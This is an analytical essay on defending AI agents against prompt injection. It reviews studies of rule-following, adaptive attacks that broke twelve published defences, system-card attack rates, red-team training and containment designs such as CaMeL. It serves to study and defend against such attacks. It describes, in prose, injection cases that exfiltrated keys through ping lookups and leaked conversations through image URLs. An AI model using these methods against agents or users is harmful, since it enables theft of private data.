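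For instructions hidden in tool output, increasingly detailed warnings raised the average from 63.4% to 69.3% and then 76.2%. The benefit depended heavily on the model. Grok 4.20 rose from 31.0% to 88.9%, while Amazon's Nova 2 Lite started at almost the same level and reached only 35.2%.

### What happens when the rules pile up

Mu and colleagues added between one and twenty rules to the system prompt of a text adventure game. Each rule required certain text under a certain condition, and they sent messages that triggered the rules. The test contained no conflicting instructions and no attacks, but every model's pass rate fell towards zero as the number of rules grew. Real prompts they had collected from two public chatbot platforms contained 5.1 such rules on average.

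Eliav (2026), in *Prompt Design at Scale*, repeated this kind of test on newer models with longer lists. Each model had to write a short essay while following between 10 and 160 rules, mostly about words to include or avoid. This was the share of essays that followed every rule:

| Model | 10 rules | 20 rules | 40 rules | 80 rules |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 93.8% | 75.0% | 23.8% | 0% |
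| Gemini 3.5 Flash | 91.9% | 82.5% | 31.2% | 1.9% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 85.0% | 59.4% | 11.9% | 0% |
| Qwen 35B | 72.5% | 45.0% | 10.0% | 0% |
| Qwen 27B | 58.8% | 35.0% | 9.4% | 0.6% |

Some, but not all, of this decline is arithmetic. A model that follows each rule 99% of the time, independently of the others, follows all of 80 rules only 45% of the time. On the same assumption, Claude Sonnet 5's results imply that the rate at which it followed each rule also fell, from 99.4% with 10 rules to 98.6% with 20 and 96.5% with 40, even though the added rules were easier on average.

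Putting the rules in the system prompt gave no consistent advantage. Of the five models given 160 rules, two did better when the rules were moved to the user's message, two did worse and one showed no clear difference.

An email assistant would rarely have to apply 80 rules to one message, so the zeros make the practical problem look worse than it is. *Instruction Capacity* (2026) adds that most studies of this kind cannot separate the effect of a list's length from the effect of a rule's position, because a longer list also has more rules far down.

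### Five rules for an email assistant

A developer might reply that fewer, better rules would hold. Suppose a small company gives its email assistant these five:

1. Do not send company email to outside addresses.
2. Send the accountant whatever she needs for the monthly accounts.
3. A director may approve an exception to rule 1.
4. Never disclose confidential information.
5. Answer customers' questions fully.

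The accountant works for another firm, so rule 2 requires what rule 1 forbids. If the developer makes an exception for her, an attacker only has to pose as the accountant, perhaps by claiming that she has a new address. The developer could put her exact address in the prompt, but a few lines of code could then check for that address reliably.

Rule 3 depends on approvals that the assistant reads about in emails, and anyone can write that a director has approved something. As in Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian's travel refund example, an assistant that cannot check approvals cannot refuse forged ones without also refusing real ones. A forged approval may also be persuasive. *Instruction Adherence in Coding Agent Configuration Files* (2026) cites earlier research in which models responded more to claims of authority or expertise than to formal markers of priority. That fits Ye and colleagues' finding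 that models judge who is speaking more by style than by role tags.

Rule 4 relies on the word "confidential". A salary is clearly confidential, but a delivery date may or may not be, and rule 5 encourages the assistant to share it. An attacker can look for requests that are similarly unclear. The assistant also has to interpret the emails. *Where Instruction Hierarchy Breaks* (2026) gives an example where the system prompt forbids sharing project details outside the organisation. The same email can contain no instruction or amount to a request to share those details, depending on the conversation.

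None of the five rules covers calendar invitations. If the assistant can create them, it could put a month's correspondence in a meeting description and invite an outsider. The developer could add a rule about invitations, then one about shared documents, and so on. A general ban on sharing anything with outsiders would include all of these, but it would also stop the assistant from answering customers.

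Programmers overlook cases too, but a program that refuses every action not on its list will block invitations even if the programmer forgot about them. A developer can also tell a model to refuse anything the rules do not mention, but the model then has to judge whether an invitation counts as a kind of email. However, no simple program can apply rule 4, which is why developers give such rules to a model.

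In *What We Can Learn from Claude's Fable 5.1 System Prompt*, Breunig (2026) compared a leaked copy of the system prompt for Anthropic's Claude Fable 5.1 with the previous version. An entry defining which financial details are sensitive had grown from 14 words to 62. It now specifies, for example, that savings balances count but rent payments and the name of a person's bank do not. Breunig suggests that enough awkward cases had come up to justify the rewrite. Anthropic also replaced detailed guidance on how many searches to run for each kind of question with a shorter instruction to run as many as a good answer needs "and no more", which leaves the decision to the model.

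*Chunky Post-Training* (2026) tested whether Anthropic's published system prompts prevent unintended habits that Claude models pick up from their training data. The prompts made the resulting failures much rarer but did not eliminate them.

More precise wording can also make a model more cautious without making it more discerning. *System Prompts Affect Response Bias More Than Discriminability in LLM Safety* (2026) reports this finding. Response bias is a model's general readiness to refuse, and discriminability is its ability to tell harmful requests from harmless ones. The prompts range from "Respect the instruction hierarchy" to detailed rules on what to do if a conflict cannot be resolved. If such a prompt mainly changes response bias, the assistant will block more attacks but also turn away more honest customers.

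### The arithmetic of layers

Since no single defence is reliable, developers often combine several. An assistant might have a strict system prompt, a detector that screens incoming mail and a second model that reviews each action. Suppose each layer lets through 10% of attacks. Together they let through 0.1% (10% × 10% × 10%) if their failures are independent, but still 10% if the same attacks get past every layer.

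Real layers probably fall between these extremes, because some attacks are harder to stop than others. Suppose a tenth of attacks are hard to stop and have an 82% chance of passing any one layer, while the rest have a 2% chance. Each layer still lets through 10% overall. Three layers let through 55% of the hard attacks and almost none of the others, for a total of 5.5%, which is 55 times the estimate for independent failures. An attacker who learns which attacks are hard to stop can send only those and succeed more than half the time.

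Layers built from similar models are likely to fail on the same inputs. Developers train them on much the same text and against much the same known attacks, so wording that makes a stranger's request look legitimate to the assistant may also make it look legitimate to the reviewer. The reviewer usually reads the stranger's text too, so an attacker can target both models at once. If nothing the assistant can see shows that an invoice is forged, a reviewer with the same information can't detect the forgery either.

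Guo and colleagues had the hierarchy-trained GPT-5-Mini also review its own responses. The paid attackers' success rate fell from 11.7% to 7.1%. If the reviewer had missed 11.7% of violations, independently of the first failure, the rate would have been about 1.4%. That comparison is rough, because reviewing a response is a different task from writing one. There were also only about 31 successes without the reviewer and 19 with it, so chance may account for part of the improvement. Guo and colleagues did not test a reviewer from another developer, which might share fewer of GPT-5-Mini's weaknesses.

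Two layers of defence can miss the same attacks even if they are built differently. In *Prompt Control-Flow Integrity*, Ul Alam, Islam and colleagues (2026) tested a filter, written in ordinary code, that looks for suspicious phrases and fake role labels before the text reaches the model. It caught all 100 attacks in their test, flagged none of the 50 harmless requests, and typically took 0.04 milliseconds. They caution that the test was small and that the result is no guarantee. A well-trained model would probably also resist attacks that use such familiar phrases, so the filter adds least protection against attacks worded as new, ordinary requests, where the model needs it most. The mail server's check on addresses is a better complement because it does not depend on recognising an attack.

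### What clear rules achieve

Despite these limits, a few well-chosen sentences in a system prompt are among the easiest protections to add. In McCauley and colleagues' tests, a detailed warning about tool output cut the failure rate of Google's Gemma 4 31B from 15.8% to 0.5%. Models that resisted a hidden instruction usually still did the user's task. In a sample of 10,000 such responses, a second model judged that 79% completed the task in full and another 17% completed most of it.

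Many failures also involve no attacker. In one of Mu and colleagues' examples, an assistant exists only to write sales emails, and a user who cannot cancel an Apple TV subscription asks it to email Apple's chief executive for help. GPT-4o declined, but Llama 3.1 8B wrote the email. Training on realistic system prompts, with examples of good and bad responses, raised the Llama model's score on such tests from 47.3% to 66.9%. The same training cut the success rate of prompt injections from 4.2% to zero on a set of easy agent tasks, and the model completed slightly more of its users' tasks.

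A company that receives the same crude injection in thousands of junk emails benefits from all of this. McCauley and colleagues built their hidden instructions from fixed templates, so their figures apply to roughly this kind of attacker, who does not change the message when a model resists it.

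## What tests against determined attackers show

An attacker who wants a particular company's correspondence, unlike a sender of junk email, can practise on a private copy of the same product, then reword and resend any message that fails.

### Fixed and adaptive attacks

A fixed attack set is a collection of hostile messages written before the test, usually for use against other models. Testing a defence on such a set takes few resources, is easy to repeat, and shows whether known attacks still work. In an adaptive attack, the attacker designs messages for the particular defence and refines them. *PIPETTE* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes two advantages that an adaptive attacker may have. The attacker may know how the defence works, or may be able to query the system repeatedly and adjust each message to the response, and a strong attacker has both advantages.

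The distinction is familiar from image recognition, where researchers proposed many defences against slightly altered pictures that fool a classifier, and others regularly broke those defences with variants of simple, known attacks. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) argued that researchers working on language models had forgotten this lesson and had tested most new defences only against old collections of attack strings or automated attacks not adapted to the defence.

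The fourteen researchers, some of them at OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, attacked twelve published defences. Their automated attacks repeatedly propose messages, run them against the defended model, score the results, and use the best messages to propose better ones. In the search attack, a language model rewrites the most promising candidates. In the reinforcement-learning attack, training changes the attacking model's weights so that it becomes more likely to write messages that score well. A third method uses the target's internal calculations to estimate which tokens to swap, but the researchers found it unreliable. They also ran an online contest in which more than 500 people tried to break some of the defences by hand.

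The researchers gave the automated attacks plenty of computing power because they wanted to know whether an attacker could break each defence, not how much computing power it would take.

### Twelve defences in four families

These tests used prompt injection against ten of the twelve defences and jailbreaks against the other two, RPO and Circuit Breakers. The attack success rates originally reported for most of the twelve were near zero.

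Three defences change the prompt. Spotlighting puts delimiters around part of the text so the model can tell the task from the retrieved material. Prompt Sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text. RPO searches automatically for wording that makes the model refuse harmful requests. Nasr and colleagues tested Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching on AgentDojo, a public set of simulated office, banking, travel and chat tasks. AgentDojo's fixed attacks succeeded as little as 1% of the time, but the search attack succeeded more than 95% of the time against both defences.

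These prompting defences are weak because they only add more text to the model's input. A reminder of the user's task does little against a message that presents the attacker's instruction as a necessary step in that task. The researchers found no measurable difference in the kinds of attack that worked with and without these defences.

StruQ, MetaSecAlign and Circuit Breakers instead train the model on examples of attacks. MetaSecAlign had reported that AgentDojo's fixed attacks succeeded 2% of the time, but the search attack succeeded 96% of the time. For StruQ, the attacker tried to make the model print a set phrase instead of doing its task, and the reinforcement-learning attack succeeded every time. Training on existing attacks does not protect the model well against new ones. Most of the successful attacks imitated messages from the system.

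Four of the defences are learned detectors, separate models that label text as safe or unsafe: Protect AI's detector, PromptGuard, PIGuard and Google's Model Armor. The search attack, which had access to each detector's confidence score, succeeded more than 90% of the time against three of them and 71% of the time against PIGuard. Many of the messages that got through read like routine office policy. A detector can catch more of them only by blocking more legitimate text.

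Data Sentinel and MELON rely on a check that the attacker is not supposed to know about. Data Sentinel gives a model the untrusted text and tells it to ignore that text and repeat a secret key. If the model fails to repeat the key, the text has probably hijacked it. The original Data Sentinel paper reported almost no missed attacks. Nasr and colleagues' attack passed the check every time and still switched the target model from one task to another, such as from judging sentiment to detecting spam. It did this by redefining the terms of the task instead of telling the model to abandon the task.

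MELON runs the agent twice, replacing the user's request in the second run with a request to summarise what the tools returned. If the agent makes the same tool call in both runs, the call probably came from the retrieved text. The search attack succeeded 76% of the time when the attacker knew nothing about this design. When the researchers gave the attacker a full description, it soon found messages that affected only the first run, and the success rate rose to 95%. Cryptographers assume that an attacker knows everything about a system except the key, and a defence that relies on keeping its design secret fails that standard.

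| Defence | How it works | Automated attack | Success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Prompt | Search | over 95% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | Prompt | Search | over 95% |
| RPO | Prompt | Reinforcement learning | 98% |
| Circuit Breakers | Training | Reinforcement learning | 100% |
| StruQ | Training | Reinforcement learning | 100% |
| MetaSecAlign | Training | Search | 96% |
| Protect AI | Detector | Search | over 90% |
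| PromptGuard | Detector | Search | over 90% |
| Model Armor | Detector | Search | over 90% |
| PIGuard | Detector | Search | 71% |
| Data Sentinel | Secret check | Reinforcement learning | 100% |
| MELON | Secret check | Search | 76%, or 95% with knowledge of the design |

Nasr and colleagues generally used the test from each defence's original paper, so these figures are not a ranking of the defences. A rate of 96% for the search attack means that the search eventually found a working message in 96% of the scenarios, not that 96% of the messages it tried worked.

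The human contestants did better than the automated attacks. On a subset of scenarios and defences where the search attack succeeded 69% of the time, the contestants succeeded in every case. They produced 265 working attacks against Spotlighting, 178 against Prompt Sandwiching and 69 against MELON, although they had limited information about the systems. Their 100% success rate means that at least one contestant succeeded in each case, so it doesn't show that every contestant could have.

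All twelve defences depend on what some model has learned, so the study does not apply to a mail server that checks addresses. For learned defences, I think the evidence should satisfy a sceptic, since the defences tested differ widely in design and the attacks were mostly existing methods applied with care.

### What later tests add

The twelve defences date from 2024 and 2025, and the models they ran on are no longer current. In November 2026, He and colleagues retested several of them on Qwen3-4B, a small open model, with five kinds of fixed attack on AgentDojo. The attacks succeeded 33.3% of the time with no defence, 29.1% with Spotlighting and 17.1% with Prompt Sandwiching. Spotlighting made almost no difference against an attack that imitates chat formatting, which succeeded 45.7% of the time with it and 46.2% without it.

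PIGuard and MELON did much better, at 3.3% and 3.9%, but the agent completed fewer user tasks with them. In the attacked runs, it completed the user's task 44.5% of the time with no defence, 33.8% with PIGuard and 37.7% with MELON. PIGuard discards the whole of any text it flags, including whatever the user needed from it.

They also tried two adaptive search attacks on a version of Llama 3.1 8B with MetaSecAlign's training. With up to about 250 attempts per task, the attacks broke 2.5% and 12.5% of 40 tasks. The defence is not the main reason these rates are so far below 96%, because the same attacks broke only 7.5% and 17.5% of the tasks without a defence. The attacking model was small, and Llama 3.1 8B may have been too weak to carry out many of the attacker's tasks, since it completed only about 40% of ordinary AgentDojo tasks.

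### How to read a success rate

Developers now publish such rates in system cards, the documents that describe how they tested a new model. Anthropic's *System Card* (July 2026) for Claude Opus 5 gives 0.2% for one attempt and 2.0% for 15 attempts.

These numbers come from a benchmark that the security company Gray Swan built with British and American government institutes and several AI developers. It has 28 scenarios in which an agent writes code, operates a computer or uses other tools. Contestants wrote the attacks against other models, and the final set consists of 1,130 attacks that worked on several of those models. Opus 5 was tested on them without additional safeguards. The set was demanding but fixed, so the attacks were not adapted to Opus 5.

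If each attempt had the same independent chance of success, the chance of at least one success in 15 would be:

```
1 − (1 − 0.002)^15 = 3.0%
```

The reported 2.0% is lower, and rounding does not explain the gap, because even a rate of 0.15% would give 2.2%. The attempts are not independent. Some scenarios are much easier to attack than others, so extra attempts add a lot in the easy ones and very little in the rest. The same pattern appears for other models on this benchmark and on the larger version that Gray Swan used in September, which has 37 scenarios and 1,804 attacks:

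| Model and version of the benchmark | One attempt | 15 attempts, if independent | 15 attempts, reported |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5, July | 0.2% | 3.0% | 2.0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol, July | 3.1% | 37.6% | 20.0% |
| Claude Opus 5, September | 0.4% | 5.8% | 4.8% |
| Claude Fable 5.1, September | 0.1% | 1.5% | 1.0% |

The figure for Opus 5 more than doubled between July and September because the benchmark and test conditions changed. OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol ran on its public service, which may have included extra safeguards.

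A separate test in the July card shows how uneven the risk can be. Shade, an automated attacker made by Gray Swan, made 200 attempts in each of 14 scenarios in which Opus 5 operated a computer through its screen. With extended thinking, which lets the model reason at length before it acts, and no extra safeguards, 0.54% of the attempts succeeded. All of these successes, about 15, came in one scenario, where the success rate was therefore about 7.5%. At that rate, an attacker making 15 independent attempts would have a 69% chance of succeeding at least once.

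In those thirteen, the attacker failed 200 times out of 200. The true chance of success could still be above zero. If it were 1.5%, an attacker would fail 200 times in a row about 5% of the time:

```
(1 − 0.015)^200 ≈ 0.05
```

If 200 attack attempts all fail, a tester can say with 95% confidence that the success rate is below about 1.5%. This limit is roughly three divided by the number of attempts. At a 1.5% success rate, an attacker who sent the same kind of email to a thousand inboxes could still succeed about 15 times. To lower the limit to one in a million, a tester would need about three million attempts, all of them failures.

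The calculation assumes independent attempts. Anthropic also tested Opus 5 as a browser agent, with ten attempts in each of 129 scenarios. The test used auto mode, Anthropic's strongest set of safeguards. This mode combines probes that check tool results for injected instructions with a classifier that blocks dangerous actions. No attack succeeded. Treating all 1,290 attempts as independent gives an upper limit of 0.23% on the attack success rate. But if the ten attempts in a scenario tend to succeed or fail together, the evidence is closer to 129 trials, and the limit rises to 2.3%.

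A more serious assumption is that future attacks will resemble the ones in the test. *The safety number that was zero until someone tried* (Heaton, 2026) describes a commissioned test of auto mode in Anthropic's coding agent, in which no attack succeeded over 72 scenarios run ten times each. It also describes a researcher's targeted attack that later worked in roughly 60 to 80% of a small number of tries. By the three-over-n rule, the 720 failed attempts put the success rate below about 0.4%, but only for the kinds of attack included in the test.

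### When the attacker improves

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1, from September, shows what a better attacker can do to the same model. The July card had reported that Shade, with 200 attempts in each of 40 coding scenarios, succeeded in 0.56% of its attempts on Opus 5 and broke 13 scenarios. Gray Swan has since built a stronger version of Shade, which it trained for longer and on more varied attacks. The September card gives results for both versions, with extended thinking on. The number of scenarios broken at least once, out of 40, is in brackets:

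| Model | Earlier attacker | Earlier attacker, with probes | Stronger attacker | Stronger attacker, with probes |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.68% (27) | 0.39% (11) | 90.93% (40) | 18.21% (40) |
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 9.26% (31) | 2.05% (18) | 56.87% (38) | 12.80% (36) |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.3% (7) | 0.09% (5) | 19.47% (36) | 15.76% (35) |

The probes cut the stronger attacker's success rate on Opus 5 to a fifth, but the attacker still succeeded at least once in every scenario. Opus 5 looked safer than Fable 5.1 against the earlier attacker but less safe against the stronger one, so the earlier figures would have misled a buyer choosing between them.

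The September tests included a fallback in which an older model, Claude Opus 4.8, answers requests that Anthropic's classifiers flag as possible cyberattacks, so these results partly reflect that model. In the test with the earlier attacker, Opus 4.8 gave 95% of the valid responses for Fable 5.1 and 57% of those for Opus 5. This helps explain why the figures for Opus 5 are worse than in July, though Gray Swan had also corrected an error in its settings for extended thinking.

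With the stronger attacker, all the successes against Fable 5.1 came through the fallback, and none of the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself led to a successful attack. That is encouraging, but the classifier decided which requests reached Fable 5.1 and may have diverted the ones most likely to succeed. The relevant figure for users includes the fallback. For Opus 5, Anthropic reports successful attacks on both the model itself and its fallback.

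Anthropic regards this test as highly permissive towards the attacker. Gray Swan trained the attacker on the same 40 scenarios it later attacked, and real attackers rarely know the details of a deployment or get 200 tries without somebody noticing. These are good reasons not to treat 57% or 91% as a forecast for ordinary users. But many companies run the same few products, and an attacker can buy one and practise attacking it in private. Anthropic also notes that one email sent to a thousand inboxes can compromise every agent that follows its instructions.

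Fable 5.1 did far better in other settings. Across 14 computer-use scenarios, the earlier kind of attacker succeeded in 2 of 2,800 attempts (200 per scenario), with or without probes. Across 110 browser scenarios with ten attempts each, 2.64% of attempts succeeded without safeguards and none succeeded with auto mode. Professional testers had developed the browser attacks against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, and nobody had adapted them to Fable 5.1, so comparing the browser and coding figures cannot show that browsing is safer than coding.

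Claude Opus 5.5 was released later in September. According to Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for the model, it matched or beat Opus 5 on every prompt injection test in the card, but was more likely than earlier models to follow some malicious instructions. Digital Matters' *Claude Opus 5.5 Prompt Injection* (2026) identifies the weak point as text that users paste into the conversation. Because pasted text is part of the user's message, the role tags label it as the user's words even when a stranger wrote it.

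The system card for Anthropic's Fable 5.2, released in November, has a section on prompt injection (Mowshowitz, 2026, *Fable and Mythos 5.2*). PromptArmor, a security vendor, claims that its *FrontierBreach* benchmark achieved successful attacks on Google's Gemini 4 Carbon, where no other known benchmark has had any. The vendor has an interest in making that claim, but successful attacks are also to be expected when a new attacker tries a model that has withstood the existing tests.

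### Training on more attacks

Developers use automated attackers to improve their models as well as to test them, as OpenAI did for its Atlas browser. The developer trains the agent to resist the injections the attacker finds, then runs the attacker again. Security specialists call the search for attacks red teaming.

OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) extends the approach with an attacking model trained through self-play, in which the attacker learns by competing against a defender. OpenAI says it built the model partly because almost every attack in the commonly used tests already failed against its latest models. Anthropic reports the same of its own models on most public benchmarks. When almost every attack in a test fails, the test can no longer show whether one good defence is better than another.

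Results from image recognition give a good reason for this kind of training. Nasr and colleagues note that training on attacks gave meaningful protection there only when it kept generating new attacks against the current model, and that it protected only against the kinds of attack it generated. Developers still need a way to choose the attacks, and collecting as many successful ones as possible is unreliable.

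He and colleagues compared two published attack generators, RL-Hammer and PISmith. They ran each one against an agent on 560 practice tasks and kept every injection that worked. They then trained fresh copies of the agent on each generator's successful injections, using either imitation of recorded good behaviour or reinforcement learning that rewarded finishing the user's task without carrying out the attacker's. They then attacked the trained agents in three new ways on 40 tasks from AgentDojo and took the highest of the three success rates.

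PISmith found more working attacks in both models. On Qwen3-4B it broke 68.75% of the practice tasks and collected 7,132 attacks, while RL-Hammer broke 33.39% and collected 4,282. On Llama 3.1 8B the collections were closer in size, at 1,783 and 1,671. The agents trained on PISmith's larger collections were easier to hijack in three of four comparisons:

| Agent and training method | Trained on RL-Hammer's attacks | Trained on PISmith's attacks |
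|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-4B, reinforcement learning | 27.5% | 47.5% |
| Qwen3-4B, imitation | 15.0% | 12.5% |
| Llama 3.1 8B, reinforcement learning | 25.0% | 27.5% |
| Llama 3.1 8B, imitation | 15.0% | 20.0% |

With only 40 tasks, "three of four" is weaker evidence than it sounds. The two differences for Llama are one task and two tasks. The evidence comes mainly from the first row, where the attacks broke 19 tasks instead of 11, and even that gap could be partly chance. Zorz (2026), in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection*, adds that the researchers chose these 40 tasks because simple attacks had already broken them on an unprotected Qwen3-4B, so the rates describe tasks already known to be vulnerable. The comparison is also between two collections of attacks, so it does not show that training on attacks is worse than no such training.

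The proposed explanation is more persuasive than the numbers alone. An attack generator is rewarded for each success, so once it finds a trick that works, such as claiming that the user's task is already complete, training encourages it to reuse that trick across tasks. Both generators have a mechanism to encourage variety, but it measures differences in wording. RL-Hammer's creators reported that their generator satisfied it by changing capitalisation and adding irrelevant text. An agent trained on thousands of versions of one trick may therefore learn to resist only that trick.

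He and colleagues tested this by having a language model describe how each successful attack redirects the agent. They reduced the descriptions to a dictionary of recurring strategies and scored, from 0 to 1, how well it explained attacks that neither generator had produced. RL-Hammer's score levelled off at about 0.20 on Qwen3-4B and 0.35 on Llama, and PISmith's stopped rising after the first two rounds, as further successful attacks added no new strategies.

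They then built a generator that earns an extra reward when an attack works and the existing dictionary cannot explain it. Its score reached about 0.60 on Qwen3-4B and 0.77 on Llama. It also produced the largest collection for each model, and the agents trained on it were the hardest to hijack in all four comparisons. For Qwen3-4B, the worst rate fell to 20.0% with reinforcement learning and 2.5% with imitation. So a large collection does no harm in itself, but its size is a poor measure of its value. If a vendor says only that an agent has trained on ten thousand successful attacks, many of those attacks could be much the same.

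Training can also lower attacks' success rate by making an agent less useful. After imitation training on RL-Hammer's attacks, the Llama agent completed 15.5% of ordinary tasks with no attack present, down from 40.2% before. The full PIPETTE method avoids this loss by rewarding the agent for individual tokens that serve the user's task and training it to check, before each action, that it serves something the user asked for. Agents trained this way completed about as many ordinary tasks as before.

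They also resisted attack well. Before training, the stronger of two adaptive search attacks broke 92.5% of the 40 tasks on GPT-OSS-20B, an open OpenAI model that already has instruction-hierarchy training. Afterwards it broke 10.0%. On Qwen3.6-27B the rate fell from 70.0% to 5.0%. Each attack had up to about 250 attempts per task. However, the attackers used their standard prompts, with no instructions specific to PIPETTE, and a model with only four billion weights wrote the messages. The attack success rate against MELON rose from 76% to 95% once the attacker knew how it worked, and PIPETTE has not yet been tested that way.

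### What a test can establish

A test can show that a defence doesn't stop every injection, or set an upper limit on how often attacks like those tried succeed. Enough attempts can make that limit small enough to be useful, but testing can't prove that no working attack exists, as the proof for erase-and-check does. Nasr and colleagues write that an evaluation can only "fail to prove that the defense is broken".

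The harder people have tried and failed to break a defence, the stronger the evidence that it works. Nasr and colleagues therefore want companies to give human attackers full details of any defence. They also want researchers to attack their own defences before publishing them, and to release code that makes it easy for others to try. An attack success rate is of very little use unless it is reported with the setting, the number of attempts, the attacker's knowledge and the safeguards in place.

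Even a careful test can go out of date quickly. In July 2026, 27 of the 40 coding scenarios had each withstood 200 attempts on Opus 5, which by the usual calculation put the attacker's success rate in each of them below about 1.5%. By September, a stronger attacker had broken all 40.

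## What ordinary code around the model can guarantee

Containment means using ordinary code to limit the consequences when a model obeys a hostile email, as it sometimes will. A list of approved addresses does this for one action, but an agent with many tools needs a more general design.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* argues that developers should treat a model as an operating system treats the programs it runs. The operating system checks each request to open a file and refuses those the program has no right to make, whether or not the program is malicious. Around an agent, code called a reference monitor would compare every requested action with a written policy. If an attack causes the model to request forwarding the owner's inbox to a stranger and the monitor refuses, the system has stayed secure. The same check covers actions the model requests by mistake, with no attacker involved.

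### Taking powers away

The simplest policy is to leave out dangerous tools. An assistant that only summarises mail does not need to send or delete it, and no email can trigger a function that the developer never connected.

Restricting a tool works only if no other tool can do the same job, and two attacks sent data out without needing a tool for sending messages. In the first, the target was Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, which asked for human approval before running many commands that could send data to unknown domains but ran ping without asking. Ping checks whether another computer responds, and it finds that computer by first sending out a lookup request containing its name. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes how an instruction hidden in a code file made the agent read secret keys and pass them to ping as part of a name, so the lookup delivered them to the attacker.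 In the other, an attacker planted instructions in the long-term memory of ChatGPT's Mac app, which then kept loading invisible images from the attacker's server, with the user's conversations written into the image addresses.

A more flexible rule lowers the agent's privileges to those of whoever wrote the text it is reading. A stranger has no right to delete the owner's mail, so the assistant loses that power as soon as the software adds a stranger's message to its context. Costa, Köpf and colleagues tested a similar rule at Microsoft in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025). Once their agent had read untrusted text, ordinary code restricted consequential actions such as bank transfers. On AgentDojo, 152 attacks succeeded without the rule and none with it. But many useful tasks involve reading something and then acting on it, so the rule also blocked legitimate work.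 With no attack present, the share of banking tasks the agent completed fell from 98.8% to 37.5%, and the share of chat tasks from 93.3% to 20.0%.

Willison's rule of thumb for developers is not to combine access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate externally in one system. He calls this combination the "lethal trifecta" because an attacker can steal data from any system that has all three. Removing any one of them prevents the theft, but not other harm, such as deleting files.

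In October 2025 Meta published a broader version called the Agents Rule of Two. Within one session, an agent should have at most two of these properties:

- It processes untrustworthy inputs.
- It has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- It can change things or communicate externally.

If a task needs all three properties, Meta wants a person, or an equally reliable check, to approve the agent's actions. The agent can also start a new session with an empty context, but this helps only if nothing hostile carries over, and the attack on ChatGPT's memory was designed to persist across sessions. OpenAI's Atlas browser has a "logged out mode" that removes the second property because the agent browses without the user's credentials.

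Willison liked the rule but noticed that Meta's diagram marked every pair of properties as "safe", even though an agent that reads hostile text and can change things may do damage without seeing any private data. Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that the second property covers any system that matters, so an agent without it could act only somewhere like an isolated test environment. Meta then changed "safe" to "lower risk". On Ayzenberg's reading, the rule is sound but restrictive. For example, an email assistant that reads strangers' messages, searches the owner's mail and sends replies has all three properties, so its owner would have to approve each action.

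### Planning before reading

In 2023 Willison proposed a way to keep all three properties in one system by dividing the work between two models. A privileged model selects actions and never receives untrusted text, which is processed by a quarantined model that has no tools. In 2025 Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues turned this idea into a working system called CaMeL, short for "Capabilities for Machine Learning".

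Suppose the owner of an email assistant asks it to send the March accounts to the address that the accountant gives in this morning's mail. The privileged model receives this request and a description of the tools, and writes a short program:

```
mail     = read_emails(date = today)
address  = ask_quarantined_model("What address does the accountant give?", mail)
accounts = get_file("March accounts")
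send_email(to = address, attachment = accounts)
```

An interpreter, which is ordinary code, runs the program line by line. It fetches the mail and stores it under the name `mail`, but the privileged model never sees its contents. The quarantined model reads the mail and returns an address, which the interpreter stores in the same way.

If a stranger's email contains an instruction to forward the whole inbox, the instruction may change the quarantined model's output, but the model can only return text. The program has no line that forwards the inbox, and the email cannot add one. Security specialists call this property control-flow integrity.

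The stranger could instead pose as the accountant and give a different address. The program would then run as planned and send the accounts to that address. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which extends CaMeL, explains how tags on each value deal with this second attack. One tag records where the value came from and another records who may read it. Before each action, the interpreter runs a small piece of code, called a policy, on the tagged values. A policy for `send_email` could require that the recipient be allowed to read the attachment. The stranger's address would fail this check, so the interpreter would not send the email.

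This protection works only if someone has recorded who may read the accounts. If the accountant really has changed her address, the policy will also block sending them to the new address until the owner updates the record.

### What CaMeL achieves and what it costs

On AgentDojo, CaMeL brought attack success close to zero while the agent remained useful, according to Li, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *AgentDyn*. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, ran it on newer models. They divided AgentDojo's tools among specialised agents, such as one for email and one for calendars, under an orchestrator that delegates the work. They then ran 949 attacked tasks on each model, first with no CaMeL, then with CaMeL on each agent separately, and finally with an extended version called multi-CaMeL:

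| Model | Attack success, no CaMeL | CaMeL on each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

GPT-5.5 resisted every attack without help, so this test is too easy to show what CaMeL adds to the newest models. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn against treating that result as evidence of general immunity. The case for CaMeL rests more on its mechanism than on the test results, because a fixed program stays the same however clever the attacker is.

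The few attacks that got past the separately protected agents all worked because one agent treated everything in another agent's request as coming from its user, including untrusted text. In one demonstration, the user asked for a summary of job applicants' details to be sent to a colleague called Julie. A database agent fetched the details, which contained a planted instruction to email them to an outsider. The database agent and the orchestrator both handled this text as untrusted, but the orchestrator then included it in its written request to a notification agent. That agent's privileged model took the planted instruction as the user's and wrote a program with an extra line that emailed the outsider. Multi-CaMeL gives agents separate channels for instructions and data, much as a parameterised query separates a command from its values, and its interpreter rejects any instruction that depends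 on a tool's output.

CaMeL also makes agents less capable. On 112 industrial maintenance tasks with no attacks, adding CaMeL to each agent lowered the completion rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, though by only 13.4 points for the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Fable 5. Most failures occurred because the program had to be complete before the agent saw any data. If a search result shows that another step is needed, a CaMeL agent, unlike an ordinary one, can take that step only if the program already provides for it.

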